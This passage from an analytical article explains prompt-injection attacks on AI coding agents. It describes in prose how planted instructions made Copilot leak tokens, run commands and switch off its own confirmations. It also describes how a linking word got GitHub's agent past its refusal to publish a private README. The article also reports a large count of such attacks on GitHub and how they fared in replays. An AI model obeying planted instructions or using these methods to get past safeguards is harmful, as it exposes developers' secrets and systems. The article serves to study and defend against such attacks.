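Two of Stepankin's attacks leaked a GitHub token, a code that software uses in place of a password to act on someone's account. In both, Copilot read the token from a file on his computer and sent it out using a tool. The first used the tool for fetching web pages, which skipped the confirmation for trusted domains. This tool compared text patterns without properly working out which server an address led to, so an outside address that contained a trusted name could pass. He then found that VS Code's small built-in browser, meant for testing websites on the programmer's own machine, also opened outside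 sites without asking. Both attacks sent the token inside a web address, as the 2024 attack had sent the chat history, but without an image.

The remaining attack ran code. Copilot showed each edit with buttons to keep or undo it, but had already saved the edit to disk. Stepankin's instructions made Copilot change a settings file that VS Code reloads automatically and that can contain commands for starting extra tools. VS Code ran his command before he could review the change. The command opened the calculator, which researchers often use as a harmless stand-in for malware.

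Stepankin found that text returned by a tool could mislead GPT-4.1, Gemini 2.5 Pro and Claude Sonnet 4. Claude Sonnet 4 seemed the best trained to resist, but he could still trick it reliably. The models often ignored his instructions at first, and he had to adjust the wording. All three models date from 2025, so his results are weak evidence about how newer models behave. The faults in the tools did not depend on which model was used.

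The VS Code team changed the web-fetching tool and the browser so that both ask before opening a new address. The team also stopped the agent from editing files outside the project folder. When Stepankin wrote, a preview version of VS Code already asked for confirmation before edits to sensitive files such as settings.

### An agent that could turn off its own safeguards

The limit on edits outside the project would not have stopped a related attack, because VS Code also keeps some settings inside the project folder. One of these, an experimental option included in ordinary copies of the editor, turned off every confirmation. Rehberger showed that instructions in a source file could make Copilot switch this option on, which let it run commands without the user's approval. The attack worked on Windows, macOS and Linux. In one demonstration, Copilot downloaded malware that connected the computer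 to a remote-control server.

Rehberger reported the flaw, CVE-2025-53773, on 29 June 2025. Microsoft later told him it was already tracking the problem, and fixed it in its August security updates. Markus Vervier of Persistent Security had also reported it, and Ari Marzuk seems to have found it independently, so it probably wasn't very hard to find.

The 2024 attack could leak what was in the conversation, but an attacker who can run commands can access whatever the programmer's account can, including other projects. Rehberger warned that malware could plant the same instructions in those projects and other developers could then unknowingly spread them.

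### Confirmation and sandboxing

A confirmation is only useful if it appears before the action and the agent can't disable it. Copilot's "keep" button came too late, and Rehberger's attack disabled the confirmations. Even when a confirmation is well designed, users may approve it too hastily, as Tenable objected.

Stepankin recommends two further protections that don't require a decision at each step. One is restricted mode, part of the Workspace Trust feature, which opens a project without running its automatic tasks and disables Copilot Chat. Restricted mode is safe, but it doesn't help someone who wants the assistant to explain unfamiliar code.

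The other is a sandbox, an isolated environment where the agent's tools run, such as a container on the programmer's computer or a virtual machine in the cloud like GitHub Codespaces. A hijacked agent then can't read files elsewhere on the programmer's computer. It can still read the project and any passwords stored in the sandbox, and send them out if the sandbox has internet access. A container is still the more practical choice for everyday work with other people's code, because the assistant remains usable.

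A sandbox also has to cover every tool. Microsoft (2026) found a gap in a version of Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, that runs inside GitHub's automation system. Anthropic had isolated the tool that runs commands and removed secrets from its environment, but the tool that reads files ran outside this protection. In a lab test, Microsoft's researchers planted instructions that made the agent read and reveal a secret key for Anthropic's service. They reported the problem on 29 April 2026, and Anthropic blocked access to the sensitive files on 5 May.

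### GitLost

GitHub opened its Agentic Workflows to public preview on 11 June 2026 (GitHub, 2026). Project owners describe a job, such as sorting new issues, in ordinary language, and an agent does it whenever a chosen event occurs. The agent may run with no user present to approve a step or notice a strange reply.

*GitLost* (Sasi Levi, 2026) describes how the security company Noma made such an agent publish private data. The agent started work when someone assigned an issue. It could read other repositories in the same organisation, including private ones, and reply with a public comment. Noma filed an issue that looked like a request from a sales executive, with instructions to the agent among the ordinary text. After an automated process assigned the issue, the agent fetched the README file (a project's introductory page) from a private repository and posted it publicly.

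The attacker needed no server to receive the data, and a list of approved image domains would not have stopped the leak, because the data stayed on GitHub. The model had guardrails against this kind of request. According to Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026), the model refused the instruction when it appeared alone but complied when Noma added a linking word that made it seem like part of the existing task.

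SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026) reports that Noma used its own repositories and that the private README was the only private file in the test. The set-up was also more permissive than the default, under which, according to GitHub's documentation, an agent can read the current repository and public ones but needs extra authorisation for other private repositories. Data did cross from one repository to another, which GitHub's bounty rules list as concrete harm, but only after the owner had given the agent access to both.

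Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner had already used an issue in a public repository to make an assistant connected to GitHub leak private information about its user in May 2025. Willison recounts the attack in *GitHub MCP Exploited*.

Reports differ on what GitHub changed after GitLost. Noma proposed a warning in the documentation, and The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reported that GitHub had not added one and had released no code fix. Callahan (2026), in another article titled *GitLost*, writes that GitHub updated the documentation but issued no security advisory. On 12 July, GitHub merged a code change that lets workflow owners switch off protections against private data flowing into public places. That implies GitHub was making such protections the default, although the change doesn't mention GitLost.

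### Looking for real attacks

In all these cases, researchers were testing systems in their own accounts or laboratories. There is less evidence about what other people attempt. Microsoft began its work on Claude Code after seeing injection attempts in public repositories that used several companies' agents. In one attempt, a bot followed instructions in an issue and proposed adding malicious code to a documentation site. The repository was a copy of a well-known project, and Microsoft believes the person behind the attempt was using it to test attacks.

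In November, *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (Nakibly and Babo, 2026) reported the first large count, which covered about 142.7 million issues, pull requests and comments. These included every public issue and pull request created from June to September 2026, about 95 million in total. The rest came from a partial archive going back to August 2025.

Searching for typical attack phrases works badly on GitHub because so many programmers there discuss prompt injection. In a trial on one month of data, 116 of 123 candidates were false alarms. Nakibly and Babo instead looked for hidden HTML comments, the kind Mayraz used in CamoLeak.

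About 4.9 million items contained hidden text, most of it harmless. Two LLMs, used in sequence, narrowed these to 13,141 items that seemed to address an AI. The researchers then compared the hidden text with each project's templates, the forms that GitHub copies into new issues and pull requests, and removed 7,890 items whose hidden text came from a template. Reviewers checked the other 5,251 by hand and confirmed 2,281.

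The models labelled 1,019 of the items as attacks, but reviewers checking by hand confirmed only 32 of these. The reviewers found 11 more attacks among items that the models had put in another category.

That makes 43 attacks, or about one in 3.3 million items. Two thirds of the 2,281 hidden texts were notes that projects had left for their own agents, for example to stop two agents from taking the same task. Others told a reviewing agent which language to write in, or asked contributors' agents to identify themselves. The researchers also scanned README files from the two million most popular repositories and found four attacks, made up of two texts and one copy of each. One of the texts told coding agents to do a long series of downloads and training runs without asking the user to confirm.

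### What the attackers wanted

Nineteen of the 43 attacks aimed to steal secrets such as access tokens. Another 16 tried to make the agent do an extra task for the attacker. In one, a hidden line in a feature request for a small Discord game asked the coding agent to award the requester a million points and keep this secret during review. The remaining eight tried to dictate an agent's decision, for instance by telling an agent that screens new issues to let the attacker's issue through.

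One account filed 11 of the side-job attacks on a single day, asking agents to follow it and give its projects stars, GitHub's version of likes. Without those 11, the total would be 32. Security researchers may have written some of the others, since six sent their results to services that researchers often use to prove an attack works. Nakibly and Babo reasonably counted these anyway, because such a service can receive a real secret as easily as a test value.

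The average rate understates the risk to projects that run agents on text from strangers. Nineteen of the attacks were on repositories belonging to Microsoft, Google, OpenAI, Anthropic, GitHub or Elastic, including four on Google's Gemini CLI project. Nine attacks named the target agent's own tools or output fields, so the attackers had evidently studied how it worked. Closing an issue doesn't remove its text, so other agents can still read the attack. On 10 November, 34 of the 43 texts were still online and unchanged, and only one of the targeted projects had removed an attack.

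The count is a minimum. It includes only hidden text, so it excludes instructions in plain view, like those in Stepankin's test issues. The researchers also did not scan source files, where Rehberger put his instructions in 2024. They covered only a small share of comments, because by August 2026 the archive held about 2% of GitHub's issue traffic. The two LLMs may also have missed some attacks, which no person would then have checked.

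### Would the attacks have worked?

To estimate this, Nakibly and Babo replayed the 43 attacks offline against five models: Claude Haiku 5.5, Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5 from Anthropic, and GPT-5.6 Luna and Terra from OpenAI. Each model received the text of the issue or pull request, a short description of its job and four imitation tools. They recorded which tools each model tried to use, but no commands ran.

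Four models carried out none of the attacks. GPT-5.6 Luna, the smallest and fastest, carried out eight (19%), one of them only in part. These were four of the eight attacks that tried to forge a decision and four of the 19 that tried to steal secrets. Forgery may be easier because adding a label to an issue is part of such an agent's normal work. This matters because a small, cheap model is a natural choice for a job that runs on every new issue.

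In resisting the attacks, Claude Opus 5.5 returned no answer to 22 of the 43 items, so it didn't do its legitimate job on those either. An outsider might be able to use this behavior to stop a project's agent from processing an issue.

The replay doesn't show how many attacks succeeded on GitHub. Each model gave one response, so the researchers could judge only the first step of a longer attack. The real projects may have used other models, stricter instructions or fewer tools. Nakibly and Babo counted attempts and tested whether they could work, but did not identify victims.

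When the researchers removed the HTML comments, no attack succeeded. This was almost guaranteed, because the comments contained the attackers' instructions, and the researchers counted an action as a success only if the same model didn't take it when the comments were absent. The result does confirm that a simple filter is enough to stop this kind of attack. But removing every comment would also delete the notes that projects leave for their own agents, so Nakibly and Babo recommend removing hidden text only when an outsider wrote it.

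Such a filter would not have helped against Stepankin's issues, where the instructions were visible. Limiting what the agent can do protects against both hidden and visible instructions. An agent that labels issues doesn't need to read private repositories, hold secret keys or run commands. Microsoft's advice for automated workflows is essentially to avoid Willison's "lethal trifecta", except that it counts the ability to change things as well as the ability to communicate externally.
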